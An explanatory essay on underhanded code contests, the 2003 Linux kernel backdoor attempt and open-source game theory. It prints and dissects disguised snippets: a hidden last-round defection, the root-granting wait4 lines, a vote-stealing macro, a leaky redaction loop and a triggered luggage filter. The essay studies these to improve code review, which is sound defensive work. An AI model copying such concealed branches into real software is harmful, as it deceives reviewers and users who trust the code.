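# Underhanded code contests and smart contract honeypots as precedents for disguised program behavior

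## What a disguised program is, and why it matters when programs read each other

Underhanded code is source code designed to look harmless to the person inspecting it but do something harmful when it runs. Programmers write it for sport in public contests, the earliest of which dates from 2004 according to *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, a survey by the security researcher David A. Wheeler (2020). Swindlers also use it to make money, notably on the Ethereum blockchain, and it has turned up in commercial products and open-source software. It also matters to game theorists who study players that are themselves programs and read one another before acting. A disguised program threatens such players because it can lead its reader to predict cooperation, then do the opposite in a case the reader overlooked.

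### A ten-round example

The Python function below plays a ten-round game in which two players simultaneously choose to cooperate (C) or defect (D) each round. The function takes two lists, its own past moves and its opponent's, and returns its next move. It appears to play tit-for-tat, which cooperates in the first round and then copies the opponent's previous move.

```python
ROUNDS = 10

def strategy(my_history, opp_history):
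    # Tit-for-tat: cooperate first, then copy the opponent's last move.
    played = len(opp_history)
    if played == 0:
        return "C"
    # A sound record holds 1 to 9 moves; if not, play safe.
    if played not in range(1, ROUNDS - 1):
        return "D"
    return opp_history[-1]
```

The first `if` covers the opening round, when no history exists, and the last line copies the opponent's latest move. Between them is a check for damaged records, which is common in real programs. The comment is right that a sound record holds 1 to 9 moves, since one move is on record in the second round and nine are on record in the tenth. `ROUNDS - 1` is 9, but Python's `range` excludes its second number, so `range(1, 9)` runs from 1 to 8. In the tenth round the list holds nine moves, so the check fails and the function returns D even if the opponent has always cooperated. An honest author would have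 written `range(1, ROUNDS)`.

The record check is the cover, the innocent reason for the suspicious lines to exist. The trigger, the condition that starts the hidden behavior, is a record of exactly nine moves, and the payload is the defection that follows. Together they make a concealed defection branch, a path through a seemingly cooperative program that ends in defection once the trigger occurs and is written so that a reader is likely to overlook it. This branch is data-triggered because its trigger lies in the input. An environment-triggered branch depends instead on the machine or its surroundings. Wheeler lists a small online contest of that kind, in which entrants wrote programs that seem to print ten numbers of a mathematical sequence but print an April Fool's greeting if the date is April 1.

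Why hide the defection in the last round? The game is a repeated Prisoner's Dilemma, and the conventional points are these:

| | Opponent cooperates | Opponent defects |
|---|---|---|
| **Player cooperates** | 3 each | 0 for the player, 5 for the opponent |
| **Player defects** | 5 for the player, 0 for the opponent | 1 each |

In a single round, defecting always scores more than cooperating, with 5 points instead of 3 against a cooperator and 1 instead of 0 against a defector. Yet two defectors get only 1 point each, while two cooperators get 3. Repetition helps because players can retaliate. If the function had defected in round five against an honest tit-for-tat player, the two would have traded retaliations to the end, and each would have finished with 27 points instead of the 30 that steady cooperation brings. By defecting in round ten, when the opponent has no chance left to retaliate,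 the function scores 32 and leaves its opponent with 27. If someone notices the fault, the author can call it an off-by-one error, which is a very common kind of bug.

### Games between programs

Tit-for-tat can punish a defection only in a later round. In an open-source game, each player submits a program that can read the other player's program before acting, so it can respond to a defector in the same round. In *Evaluating LLMs in Open-Source Games*, Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner (2025) have language models write the programs, using the same points as above. The theory dates back at least to *Program Equilibrium* (Tennenholtz, 2004), which starts from John von Neumann's observation that a computer program is both a set of instructions and a file that other programs can read and compare. Its solution to the one-round Prisoner's Dilemma is a program that cooperates if the other player's program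 is identical to it and defects otherwise.

If both players submit that program, the texts match and each player gets 3. If one player submits anything else, the texts differ, the remaining copy defects, and the player who switched gets at most 1. So neither player gains by replacing only their own program, and Tennenholtz named any set of submitted programs with this property a program equilibrium. Mutual defection is still an equilibrium, but no longer the only one. He also proved that in any finite game, if an outcome gives each player at least what that player could secure against opponents trying to minimize their score, some program equilibrium produces it.

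Barasz, Christiano and colleagues (2014), in *Robust Cooperation in the Prisoner's Dilemma*, trace the copy-matching program to work by Howard and McAfee in the 1980s and call it CliqueBot. No disguise works against it, because a concealed branch changes the text and CliqueBot defects if even one character differs. But it gets this safety by never judging behavior, so it also defects against harmless variants of itself. Critch (2016), in *Parametric Bounded Löb's Theorem and Robust Cooperation of Bounded Agents*, pointed out that one added comment is enough to make two cooperating copies defect against each other. Levine (2026), in *Math for AI safety*, makes the same objection about a program that behaves identically but is formatted differently or written in another language. To cooperate with strangers, a program must predict from a stranger's text what the stranger will do, and a concealed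 branch can make that prediction wrong.

*Cooperative and uncooperative institution designs* (Critch, Dennis and Russell, 2022) describes two programs that search for proofs about their opponent's behavior before deciding whether to cooperate. They have opposite defaults. DUPOC, short for "Defect Unless Proof of Cooperation", searches every possible proof up to *k* characters long for one showing that its opponent will cooperate with it, and cooperates only if it finds one. CUPOD, "Cooperate Unless Proof of Defection", searches for a proof that the opponent will defect, and cooperates if it finds none. If the proof system proves only true statements, no opponent can exploit DUPOC, because it never cooperates without a proof that the opponent will too. CUPOD can be exploited. In one of the paper's examples, it plays against a program that always defects. With a limit of ten characters, CUPOD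 cooperates and gets 0, because no proof is that short. With a limit of a billion characters, it finds the proof and defects.

Most human code review resembles CUPOD: the reviewer approves unless some fault comes to light. A concealed defection branch is a way of pushing the proof of defection beyond the reviewer's budget of time and attention. The obvious remedy is to copy DUPOC, though at first sight DUPOC looks too strict to be any use, because two copies of it would each be waiting for a proof about the other. They cooperate all the same once *k* is large enough. The argument is easiest to follow for FairBot, the idealized version that Barasz and colleagues studied, which searches proofs of any length. Let φ be the sentence "both programs cooperate", and write □φ for "φ has a proof". If φ has a proof, both programs find what they are looking for and cooperate, which makes φ true. So □φ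 → φ holds, and one can prove that it holds just by inspecting the two programs. Löb's theorem, a result in mathematical logic, covers exactly this situation:

if ⊢ (□φ → φ), then ⊢ φ.

Here ⊢ means "the system proves". The proof of φ therefore exists, both searches succeed, and both programs cooperate, even if they are written in different languages. *Formalization, Transparency, and Collusion in Open-Source Game Theory* (Duclaux, Formenti and colleagues, 2026) formalizes the theory of such programs, with limits on proof length, in the proof checker Lean. It also reports Prisoner's Dilemma experiments in which cooperation rose as programs got more information about each other. That result concerns how much a program learns about its opponent, and a disguised opponent can share its complete text without making its behavior clear.

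A program can also run its opponent instead of proving things about it. Cooper, Oesterheld and Conitzer (2024) point out in *Characterising Simulation-Based Program Equilibria* that this approach works even on programs that are hard to interpret. They analyze programs that simulate the other player and respond to the result, with a small chance of acting without simulation so that two of them do not simulate each other forever. Simulation avoids the danger of misreading a program, but it shows only the case that somebody chose to run. For example, a nine-round trial of the function above would show flawless tit-for-tat.

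### Underhanded and obfuscated code

Obfuscated code, unlike underhanded code, is openly hard to read. Wheeler's example is a tool that turns any JavaScript program into a long string of just six punctuation marks. Nobody could review the output or think they had understood it. In 2021, a participant on an open-source security mailing list suggested that the contest for obfuscated C programs, which goes back to 1984, was related to underhanded code. Wheeler (2021), in *Re: Trojan Source Attacks*, granted that one could argue so, and thought the C contest had heavily inspired the first underhanded one in 2004. But he considered underhanded code significantly different. He wrote that it is usually "painfully obvious" that entries to the C contest are hard to read, whereas underhanded code is meant to be "easy to understand WRONGLY", looking innocent while doing something malevolent.

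His survey of the year before had left obfuscated code out for this reason. A reviewer who meets it can report that it is hard to understand and refuse to trust it on that ground alone. Underhanded code gives no such warning, because the reader comes away with an explanation that seems complete. (The 2004 contest bore the name Obfuscated V, which is unfortunate, since its entries were underhanded in Wheeler's sense.)

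Knowing more programming languages can make a reader more likely to misread a program. Wheeler describes a Python sample that relies on the two characters `//`. In many languages they start a comment, which the computer ignores, but in Python they don't, so what looks like a comment is code that runs. An experienced programmer who knows several languages would probably fall for this, while a beginner who knew only Python would have no reason to. Wheeler himself missed it even in an editor that colors comments differently from code. The `range` trick exploits a similar habit, reading "1 to 9" as including the 9.

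### What Rice's theorem rules out

No reader can detect every possible disguise. A theorem Rice (1953) proved in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems* implies that, for any property of behavior that some programs have and others lack, no general method can decide, for every program, whether it has that property. "Never defects against a cooperator" is such a property.

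*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from the Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER) in Cambridge, gives the core of the reasoning in a few lines of code. A new program runs an arbitrary program and then, if that program finishes, performs a forbidden action. The forbidden action happens exactly when the arbitrary program finishes, so a method that could always tell whether the action happens could also tell whether any program finishes. An earlier result, the undecidability of the halting problem, shows that no method can do that.

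Rice's theorem rules out a single method that works for every program, but a reader usually has one particular program to check. *Rice's Theorem says that AIs can't determine much*, a post on the forum LessWrong, applies the theorem to agents that hold each other's source code, and the conclusion in its title goes further than the theorem does. Rice himself added, right after the starkest statement of the result, "Of course there will exist special methods for particular functions." The CSER response gives a good analogy from mathematics. No procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement, but Pythagoras's theorem still has a proof.

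The ten-round function can be tested on every possible input. Its move depends only on the opponent's record, and a ten-round match allows 1,023 such records, from the empty list up to the 512 possible lists of nine moves. A tester can run the function on all of them in a fraction of a second and expose the disguise by comparing the answers with real tit-for-tat. They differ in 256 cases, all in the last round. In a 200-round match there would be around 10^60 records, so the tester would have to reason about the code instead.

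Static analysis means reasoning about a program without running it. Møller and Schwartzbach (2024), in *Static Program Analysis*, explain that results by Turing and Rice generally force such analysis to approximate, but that the right kind of approximation can still guarantee something about all possible executions. The analysis will be inconclusive for some programs, and deciding how to treat them is again the choice between DUPOC and CUPOD. Rice's theorem rules out a reader who judges every program correctly, but a reader who rejects every program the analysis can't clear will still catch every disguised one, provided the analysis is sound. The detection rate (the share of disguised programs that the reader flags) is then 100%, but the reader will also wrongly flag some honest programs, and the share of honest programs it flags is its false positive rate.

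The drawbacks of that strictness depend partly on the people who write honest programs, who can choose forms that are easy to check, as CSER observes. Tennenholtz's programs contain no loops, so they always finish. Barasz and colleagues define a restricted class of programs, and an algorithm can compute the moves these programs make against each other. If players agree to submit only programs like these, Rice's theorem no longer rules out a reliable check, but the players give up whatever they could have done with the rest of the language.

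### Contests and honeypots as evidence

This theory doesn't predict how often readers miss disguises in practice. Ordinary software is a poor place to find out, because if `range(1, ROUNDS - 1)` turned up in a company's code, nobody could tell whether the author intended it, or count it as a deception that succeeded or failed. Contests are more useful because the code is public, somebody has tried to read it, and the author or the judges explain the trick. The Underhanded C Contest, for instance, asked for innocent-looking programs with malicious behavior, and its judges published and discussed the best of them.

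Contest results are biased evidence of how often reviewers detect disguised programs. Wheeler found that the Obfuscated V organizer had put every judged entry online, but the Underhanded C website covered mainly winners and runners-up. He asked for the full set of entries and had not received it when he published. Failed disguises are therefore underrepresented on that site, so it can't be used to calculate a detection rate. Contest judges also know beforehand that each program hides something, while a reviewer at work does not.

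Honeypot contracts are closer to ordinary conditions in one respect, because the reader has money at stake. A smart contract is a program stored and run on a blockchain, where it can hold and pay out money. A honeypot contract appears to have a flaw that would let someone steal its money, but a hidden trap keeps whatever the would-be thief sends to it. He can read the code for as long as he likes before sending anything, and if he misreads it, the blockchain publicly records his loss.

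## Hidden vote-stealing code and the first tests of reviewers, 2003 to 2007

A programmer who writes a suspicious line of code can usually call it a mistake. That excuse was hard to believe for two lines found in the Linux kernel's code in November 2003, because somebody had apparently broken into a server to insert them. The kernel is the core of the operating system and controls what every other program may do. Its developers kept the master copy of the code in BitMover's BitKeeper system. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so there was also a duplicate in another system, CVS. The intruder altered only the duplicate.

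### One missing equals sign

The two lines went into `wait4`, a function that programs call when they need to wait for something:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

In *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013), the computer scientist Ed Felten explains that an expert reading this code casually would take it for harmless error checking. The first half of the condition checks whether the calling program has passed two particular options together, which the documentation forbids. The second half appears to check whether the program is running as user 0, the administrator or "root", who may do anything on the machine. But it uses `=`, which assigns a value in the programming language C, instead of `==`, which compares two values, so it makes the calling program root.

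C evaluates the second half of the condition only if the first half is true, so normal calls to `wait4` are unaffected. An assignment in C has a value, in this case 0, which counts as false. The whole condition is therefore false, so the function never reports the error and the calling program continues with full control of the machine. The error check is the cover, the pair of forbidden options is the trigger, and the payload is the assignment inside the condition, where a reader expects a comparison.

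BitMover found the change by comparing files, without anybody understanding it. Larry McVoy of BitMover said the company built the CVS copy on its own machine, sent the updated files to the public server, and then compared checksums (short codes computed from a file's contents) at both ends. One file did not match. McVoy reported this to the kernel developers' mailing list in *BK2CVS problem* (2003) and said that the file's history had some extra entries under the user name davem. One entry contained an apology for working on the wrong file. Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered* (2003) identified davem as David Miller, a long-time Linux developer to whom the intruder had falsely attributed the changes, and added that the master copy had never been at risk. According to Freedom to Tinker, nobody knows who the intruder was.

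The messages that followed show how experts read the lines, though all of them already knew that an intruder had planted the code. When another developer asked what had changed, McVoy posted the lines. The first response, a few minutes later, was "That looks odd", to which Andries Brouwer replied, "Not if you hope to get root." About twenty minutes after the lines appeared, Chad Kitching explained what they did. He had also noticed that the error check was pointless, since the next line of the function replaced the error code with a different one. McVoy answered, "Good eyes, I missed that."

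Like CliqueBot, the checksum comparison only checked whether two texts were the same, so disguising the code could not have helped the intruder. But the comparison needed a trusted original. A reviewer who receives new code from its author has no such original and must read the code.

Jones (2003), in *How a backdoor in the Linux kernel was thwarted, from RISKS*, connected the kernel attack to elections within a week. US officials were then buying voting machines that recorded votes only electronically, and examiners inspected the proprietary source code in private. Jones, a computer scientist at the University of Iowa, called the attack a good example of what those examiners had to be ready for. The standards for voting systems already banned assignments inside conditions, and existing checks were good at finding them, but he expected an attacker this skilled to follow the coding rules strictly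 and hide the attack in some other way.

### The Obfuscated V Contest

In October, Daniel Horn (2004), in *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest*, invited programmers to write C code that looks correct but miscounts votes. He credited the contest for obfuscated C programs and the scandals over electronic voting as inspiration. Under the rules, set out in *The Obfuscated V contest*, a program reads a string of letters and counts K for Kerry, B for Bush and N for Nader, the main candidates in that year's presidential election. It ignores blanks and counts anything else as "Other". Horn supplied an honest version with roughly the expected structure for entrants to corrupt.

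One category was for programs that always favored a candidate, and the other was for programs that counted correctly until Election Day, November 2, and cheated only then. Horn promised to run the second kind on November 1 and to require a correct tally. On November 2 judges would read the programs in each category and run them one at a time, starting with the one that looked most correct. The first to miscount would win. An entry earned bonus points if it gave votes to the wrong candidates but kept the total number of votes right. The prize was a CD of the video game Vega Strike.

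The Election Day programs have branches triggered by their environment. The better entrants avoided an explicit comparison with November 2, because that would be an obvious thing for a reviewer to look for.

Paul Parkanzky's winning entry in this category relied on the spelling of a date. The program writes a message containing the day of the month as a word into an array that is too small. "Second" has six letters, one more than "first" or "third", so on November 2 the message overruns the array and overwrites neighboring memory, and Bush gains votes. A reader may notice that the array is too small, a common and usually innocent mistake, without connecting it to the election.

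Michal Zalewski won the other category with a trick that needs no date. In C, `#define` creates a macro, a name that the compiler replaces with a piece of program text before translating the program. The following is a much shortened imitation of his code:

```c
#define ADD_VOTE(c) {                     \
        struct candidate *t = tally;      \
        (c)->votes++;                     \
        while (t->name) check(t++);       \
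    }

for (t = tally; t->name; t++)
    if (t->letter == ballot)
        ADD_VOTE(t);
```

The loop at the bottom goes through the list of candidates, using `t` to mark the current one. When it reaches the candidate whose letter is on the ballot, it passes `t` to the macro, which seems to add a vote for that candidate and then check every entry in the list. But the macro creates its own `t`, which starts at the top of the list. Because a macro only substitutes text, its second line becomes `(t)->votes++`, which uses the new `t` and gives the vote to the first candidate on the list. Zalewski's program took this faulty path only a tenth of the time, which gave Bush some extra votes without making the result absurd.

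Matthew Eastman, who came close to winning the Election Day category, exploited one of C's more confusing features. His function for checking the date receives a pointer, which is the memory address of the current time. The instruction `givenTime--` moves this pointer back to whatever comes before the time in memory, which in this program is the voting data. The comments lead the reader to think that the instruction makes the time one second earlier, which would require `(*givenTime)--`. A later line, which also has a plausible comment, then overwrites the voting data.

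The judges scored entries out of 10 for creativity, believability and a plausible count. Zalewski received the highest score, 7.3, and Parkanzky received 7.0. Programs that replaced `==` with `=`, the trick from the kernel attack, scored near the bottom, with 3.3 points each.

### Forty disguises and fifteen remedies

In his 2020 survey, Wheeler went through the contest's judged entries to find out which precautions would have exposed them. He began by looking for the harmful lines, with the organizers' one-sentence explanations as a guide, and ran into trouble. Four of the explanations were wrong, misleading or about attack code that was missing:

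- For Ryan Cumings's program, the organizers blamed a swap of the letter O and the digit 0. The swap is there, but the main fault is the expression `vote % 2`, which can only be 0 or 1 and so directs every vote to the first two rows of the table.
- Travis Fisher's code is honest as written. The attack was in the command for compiling it, which Horn had lost. He later supplied a substitute that redefines the standard test for a blank character so that it is true of the letter K.
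- Geir Thomassen's published program works correctly, and the macro in the organizers' explanation does not exist.
- Brad Grzesiak's entry was described as "gets instead of equals". C has a function named `gets`, but the program never uses it. The explanation probably meant `=` instead of `==`.

Wheeler took this as a sign that such code is hard to find, even for people who know it is malicious and have a hint about the method. The Cumings case supports him best, because the organizers had the code and still chose the wrong suspicious line. Fisher's and Thomassen's entries may show only that the organizers kept poor records.

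He dropped Thomassen's program, which left 40 samples, 9 that waited for Election Day and 31 that did not. (Two were his own, since he had entered the contest himself.) Of the 40, 25 fell into five families:

| Trick | Samples | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Misuse of `#define` | 9 | Zalewski's macro with its own `t` |
| Look-alike characters | 7 | A variable named `l` in place of the digit `1` |
| Reading or writing outside an array | 5 | Parkanzky's message containing "second" |
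| Code hidden in comments | 2 | A comment that ends earlier than its layout suggests |
| `=` in place of `==` | 2 | A test that turns every vote into one for Kerry |

Many of these are mistakes that honest programmers make too. That gives the reviewer an advantage, because software companies have spent decades building tools to catch common mistakes. Wheeler listed 15 possible countermeasures, and they come in a few broad kinds. Some make the text harder to misread:

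- editors that color code and use fonts with distinct characters
- a rule that comments must have lines to themselves
- automatic reformatting to a layout that the author does not control
- bans on confusable characters, and on unexpected characters of any sort

Others look for faults in the code or in its behavior:

- compiler warnings and style checkers
- security analyzers that examine the code without running it
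- tools that detect memory errors while a program runs
- fuzzing, which means running the program on masses of generated inputs
- tests that exercise as much of the code as possible

The remaining measures change what programmers may write or how they work. A project can restrict dangerous constructs such as `#define`, give safe meanings to constructs that the language leaves undefined, switch to a language with fewer traps, or amend the language. The developers of Solidity, a language for smart contracts, amended theirs after a contest of their own. The last measure is to keep studying new tricks.

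He chose five measures to try on the 40 samples. With many of its warnings switched on, the compiler gcc flagged the harmful line in 15 samples. Strict limits on `#define` would stop 9, and a ban on names made of lowercase l or capital O would stop 8. The memory checker AddressSanitizer would expose 5, and coloring and reformatting comments would expose 2. Some samples are counted under two measures, so together the five detect 30 of the 40, or 75%.

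It should have been 31. Kristian Nielsen's program indents its lines so that a loop appears to cover less than it does. gcc has a warning for this, but the warning failed to appear, and Wheeler reported the bug to the warning's developer.

He judged that six of the other nine would make a reviewer suspicious even if the reviewer could not find the fault. One of the six was his own, which simply contains a second, almost identical block of code for Election Day. Only three samples, 7.5%, looked innocent and got past all five measures:

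- Matthew Russotto's program fills in a table but takes the length from a different, shorter one, so most of the table keeps an odd starting value.
- Robert Seace's program converts a list of large numbers to the wrong type and then counts votes in it as though each entry were a single byte.
- Jared Sohn's program asks whether a vote is "n" or "n", where it should ask about "n" or "N", so Nader's votes go to "Other".

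None of the three cheats only on Election Day. Wheeler observed that good tests could expose every program that cheats regardless of the date, so ordinary testing would probably have caught these as well. Testing is weakest against programs triggered by a date. Wheeler's five measures did fairly well against those, stopping seven of the nine, although compiler warnings stopped only two of those seven.

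### What the 75 percent rests on

Wheeler called 75% remarkably high for such simple measures and concluded that countering underhanded code is not impossible. He acknowledged that some might consider his method unfair, because he had studied the tricks first and then picked countermeasures partly based on what he found. He said he only wanted to show that a small set of general measures can often detect such code.

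That is a fair defense of the modest claim, but it means the 75% describes how well the measures fit the tricks of 2004 and does not predict how well they would work against new ones. The entrants also had no chance to adapt. They wrote for gcc versions 2.95 to 3.4, as Horn's rules required, while Wheeler used version 7.5.0. A real attacker can run the reviewer's compiler first and rewrite the code until the warnings stop.

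The kernel attack shows how little rewriting that can take. Both contest entries that used `=` for `==` set off a gcc warning, and Wheeler recommended the same warning against the trick. Programmers can suppress it by putting an extra pair of parentheses around the assignment, to signal that it is deliberate. The intruder's `(current->uid = 0)` has those parentheses, and on the day of the discovery the developer Tomas Szepe pointed out that they avoid a gcc warning. They also don't look strange, because many programmers would put them around an ordinary comparison. So the warning that flagged this trick in the contest would have missed the best-known real attack that used it. A tool that reports unreachable code might have caught the attack, because the line returning the error could never run. Wheeler's longer list included this check too, but the gcc option for it no longer worked.

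About half of the 30 detections also rest at least partly on Wheeler's judgment rather than on tests. He ran gcc on every sample, but he didn't have time to run AddressSanitizer on all of them, so he estimated the remaining results from how the tool works. He had no tool to check the ban on look-alike letters, and human reviewers would have to enforce the limits on `#define`. In most cases his judgment seems safe, since a rule such as the ban on variables named `l` should catch any program that depends on one.

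Every sample was disguised, so the trial could not yield a false positive rate, which matters because reviewers switch off or ignore tools that raise too many alarms. Wheeler saw many gcc warnings about unrelated slips in the samples and rightly did not count them as detections, but a reviewer would have to sort through them all. He cites an earlier complaint about false alarms from MISRA C, a set of rules for safety-critical programs. Les Hatton applied the 2004 edition to real code and found the ratio of real problems to false alarms "unacceptably low". Defenders of MISRA C answer that its purpose is to prevent errors, not to find them, so an alarm puts the burden of proof on the programmer to justify an unusual construct, as with DUPOC.

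A better reason for optimism than the number is Wheeler's argument that underhanded code has to do one particular wrong thing while looking as though it does the right thing. Each rule that closes off a family of tricks makes it harder to do both. He suggested keeping some countermeasures secret so that an attacker could not check the code against all of them beforehand, and he thought that even an imperfect defense could deter people who fear exposure. The approach is weakest where review requires specialist expertise. In a separate contest for underhanded cryptography, many winners exploited faults in the mathematics or design of the encryption, which rules about letters or macros would not catch. Wheeler concluded that specialists have to review such code in depth.

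He also became faster at spotting attacks as he worked through the entries, and suggested that training on samples could greatly improve reviewers. The evidence for this is weak, as he more or less admits, because the entries were sorted from hardest to easiest and he would have sped up anyway.

### Student auditors at Rice University

Hack-a-Vote, an exercise in a graduate security course at Rice University, had already tested human reviewers more systematically. The instructors wrote a clean, well-commented demonstration voting machine in about 2,000 lines of Java. Twelve students, working in pairs, spent two weeks corrupting it as if someone had paid them to rig an election without getting caught. Each pair then had one week, alongside their other work, to find what was wrong in the programs of two other pairs. They knew the original program from corrupting it themselves, but the university's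 honor code forbade them to compare the files directly, because that would have revealed the changes.

Several pairs hid their attacks from testers as well as from people reading the code. One pair's code added votes for a favored party only on machines with an identification number above two, because the pair assumed a tester would set up no more than two machines. Another pair's attack began only after a certain number of people had voted. Other pairs attacked the PIN that lets each person vote once, the shuffling that keeps ballots anonymous, or the machine's ability to run.

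The subtlest attack changed how the program checks whether two candidates are the same person. Java programs often keep their counts in a hash table, which uses two functions to tell one entry from another. The students rewrote both functions to treat two candidates as the same if one's name began with the other's. The program would count correctly with most lists of names, but if the candidates included, say, a Brown and a Browning, one would receive both candidates' votes and the other would be missing from the results.

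Two pairs audited each program. Both pairs found the hack in about two thirds of cases, and one pair found it in all but one of the rest, so a pair working alone would have found roughly four hacks in five. The hack that neither pair found was an extra option for starting the voting machine, which cut its connection to the console that checks PINs. Auditors sometimes noticed altered code without working out its purpose, as with the hash table attack, although a bug in that attack may have confused them.

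Four in five is a good detection rate for part-time students who had a week, but the conditions made their task easier. The program was short and familiar, the rules barred the saboteurs from rewriting large parts of it, and the auditors knew that every copy had been tampered with. Because the exercise included no clean copies, it could not show how often the auditors would have wrongly flagged one. The code for a real voting machine made by Diebold was more than 50,000 lines long. An employee of SAIC, a company that had reviewed that code, said that hiding something malicious in it would be easy and put the chance of its going undetected at 99.9%. That figure was an expert's guess, but the Rice instructors agreed that auditing alone was not enough to secure an election.

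They proposed that voting machines print each vote on paper for the voter to check, and that the paper count as the official record. Wheeler describes voter-verifiable paper ballots as the minimum that experts widely agree on. A hidden branch in the code could still falsify the electronic tally, but officials could find the discrepancy by counting the printouts by hand, without reading any code.

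## The Underhanded C Contest, 2005 to 2014

Horn's vote-counting contest impressed Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University. He started the Underhanded C Contest in 2005 and paid for it himself. In the contest's *FAQ*, he writes that its purpose is partly to identify underhanded tactics and explore what makes them possible. He denies that he wants to discredit open-source software, and says that if anything the contest illustrates a need for "more code review, not less".

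Every contest called for a program that performed a simple data-processing task while secretly misbehaving in a specified way. Craver (2014), in *The 7th Underhanded C Contest is now Open*, lists what earned points. Short, readable code scored higher because hiding a bug there is more impressive. Under the 2007 rules, a source file of more than 200 lines was unlikely to win (Shostack + Friends, *Weak Crypto Contest*, 2007). The code also had to look innocent under an editor's syntax coloring. Confusing an `l` with a `1` counted for as much as an obscure quirk of the language. The flaw had to be plausibly deniable, so that if someone found it, it would look like an innocent error, or "a newbie coding mistake", as the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* page puts it.

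### Deniability

A reviewer who finds such a flaw knows what the program does, but not whether its author meant it. Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, build their definitions around this problem. They call a backdoor intentional if the code contains an explicit path from the trigger to the payload, such as a login check that also accepts one fixed password. If the path exists only because of an apparent bug, such as a write past the end of an array, they call it a deniable backdoor when non-technical evidence suggests intent, and an accidental vulnerability when there is no such evidence. Nobody can tell these two apart on technical grounds alone. In the Linux kernel attack of 2003, the missing equals sign could have been a mistake, but the break-in and the forged user name suggested intent.

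Thomas and Francillon also analyzed eleven real backdoors, several of them in home routers, and found none deniable. One D-Link router let in any browser that identified itself with a string that, read backward, begins "editby04882joelbackdoor". This sample can't establish whether real attackers are clumsier than Craver's contestants, because people who find a well-made deniable backdoor probably record it as a bug, which keeps it off lists of backdoors.

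A player in an open-source game that finds a defecting branch in its opponent's code can defect too, whatever the author intended. Intent matters to a reviewer who has to decide whether to trust the author's next contribution. If a disguise fails but the flaw looks like a beginner's error, the author can apologize, fix it and try again, so deniability makes the consequences of failure less serious.

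### Seven challenges

| Year | Task | Secret misdeed | Winner |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2005 | Process an image, for example by blurring it | Hide a different fingerprint in every output | Natori Shin; M Joonas Pihlaja and Paul V-Khuong |
| 2006 | Count how often each word occurs in a text | Run absurdly slowly on one operating system | Bobby Brogan |
| 2007 | Encrypt a file | Encrypt between 1% and 0.01% of files weakly | Emmanuel Colbus |
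| 2008 | Black out rectangles in an image | Leave the hidden parts recoverable | John Meacham |
| 2009 | Look up airline luggage records | Misroute a bag if a clerk types the right comment | Sam Blackburn |
| 2013 | Measure how closely two users of a social network are linked | Give the author access to strangers' accounts | Alex Olson |
| 2014 | Scan messages for government surveillance | Let the users under surveillance find out | Karen Pease |

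The gap after 2009 was unplanned. Craver announced the 2009 winners, with apologies, on April 1, 2013, and opened the next contest the same day.

A program that misbehaved often and visibly would fail its first test. Some challenges avoided this with a rare trigger, such as the clerk's comment in 2009. In 2005 and 2008 the program could misbehave on every run, because nobody would see the effect by looking at the picture. A program that plays the Prisoner's Dilemma can't hide a defection this way, because the other player sees every move, so the entries with rare triggers are the closer precedent for a concealed defection branch.

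### Black pixels that leak

Meacham's winning program from 2008 has 55 lines. It reads images in a plain-text version of the PPM format, which describes each pixel by three numbers, for red, green and blue. Leaving out the lines that keep track of the position in the image, the main loop amounts to this:

```c
for (c = buf; *c; c++) {
    if (isdigit(*c) && in_rectangle(x, y))
        putchar('0');
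    else
        putchar(*c);
}
```

The loop goes through the file one character at a time. If the character is a digit and belongs to a pixel inside the rectangle, the program writes a 0. Otherwise it copies the character unchanged.

This code replaces every digit in the rectangle with a zero, though a reader would expect it to replace every number. A 7 becomes 0, a 42 becomes 00 and a 255 becomes 000. These all equal zero, which means black, so the rectangle looks black on the screen, but the file still records how many digits each number had. In a scan of black print on white paper, the black pixels become 0 and the white ones 000, which is enough to make the print legible again. The leak needs no special trigger and occurs whenever someone uses the program for its stated purpose.

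Many other entrants scrambled the pixels with a recoverable mask or appended the original data to the file. Craver (2009), in *2008 Winners*, thought that masking would always look a bit odd and that someone might notice the extra data. Meacham's program removes the pixels in the most obvious way and doesn't change the file size. Meacham also had a good excuse for its design. He commented that he had to work character by character to get around a problem with `fgets`, C's standard function for reading a line, and that a version without the leak would have been more complicated or buggy. A reviewer who opened an output file in a text editor would have seen the rows of 0 and 000, but someone checking redactions would naturally look at the image.

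### A comment that begins with zero

In the 2009 challenge, each luggage record holds a time, a luggage number, a flight, two airports and a free comment. The user types four patterns, with a hyphen for "anything", and the program prints the current records that match. A check-in clerk who wants to misroute a bag controls only the comment. The runner-up known as RHays solved this in 71 lines, of which these are the important ones, slightly simplified:

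```c
/* treat NULL as an empty string, for safety */
static int safe_strcmp(const char *x, const char *y) {
    if (x == NULL || y == NULL)
        return (y != NULL && *y != '\0')
            || (x != NULL && *x == '0');
    return strcmp(x, y);
}

for (i = 0; i < 5; ++i)
    if (safe_strcmp(argv[i+1], "-") &&
        safe_strcmp(field[i+1], argv[i+1]))
        return;    /* no match, so don't print */
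```

The standard function `strcmp` returns 0 if two strings are equal. It may crash if given NULL, C's value for a pointer that points to nothing, and `safe_strcmp` appears to be a sensible wrapper that prevents this. The user's four patterns are in `argv[1]` to `argv[4]`, and the matching parts of the record in `field[1]` to `field[4]`. A reader expects the loop to compare the four pairs and skip the record if any pair differs.

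But the loop runs five times. On the last pass it compares `field[5]`, the comment, with `argv[5]`, which is NULL because the user typed only four patterns. The wrapper should then check whether the comment is empty by looking for `'\0'`, the character that ends every string in C, but it looks for `'0'`, the digit zero. It therefore reports a difference only if the comment begins with a zero, and the record then silently disappears from the output. The contest site's example is a comment that starts "0ffered passenger compensation", with a zero in place of the O.

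Each mistake hides the other. If the wrapper worked correctly, it would report that any non-empty comment differs from an empty string, the extra pass would suppress every record with a comment, and somebody would notice at once. With the wrong character in the wrapper, the extra pass has no effect until the trigger arrives. RHays also added three automatic checks of `safe_strcmp`, which it passes because they use only NULL and empty strings, the cases it handles correctly. The faulty condition in the original also contains some unnecessary terms. Craver thought these terms set up a pattern that fools the eye and made the code look just amateurish enough.

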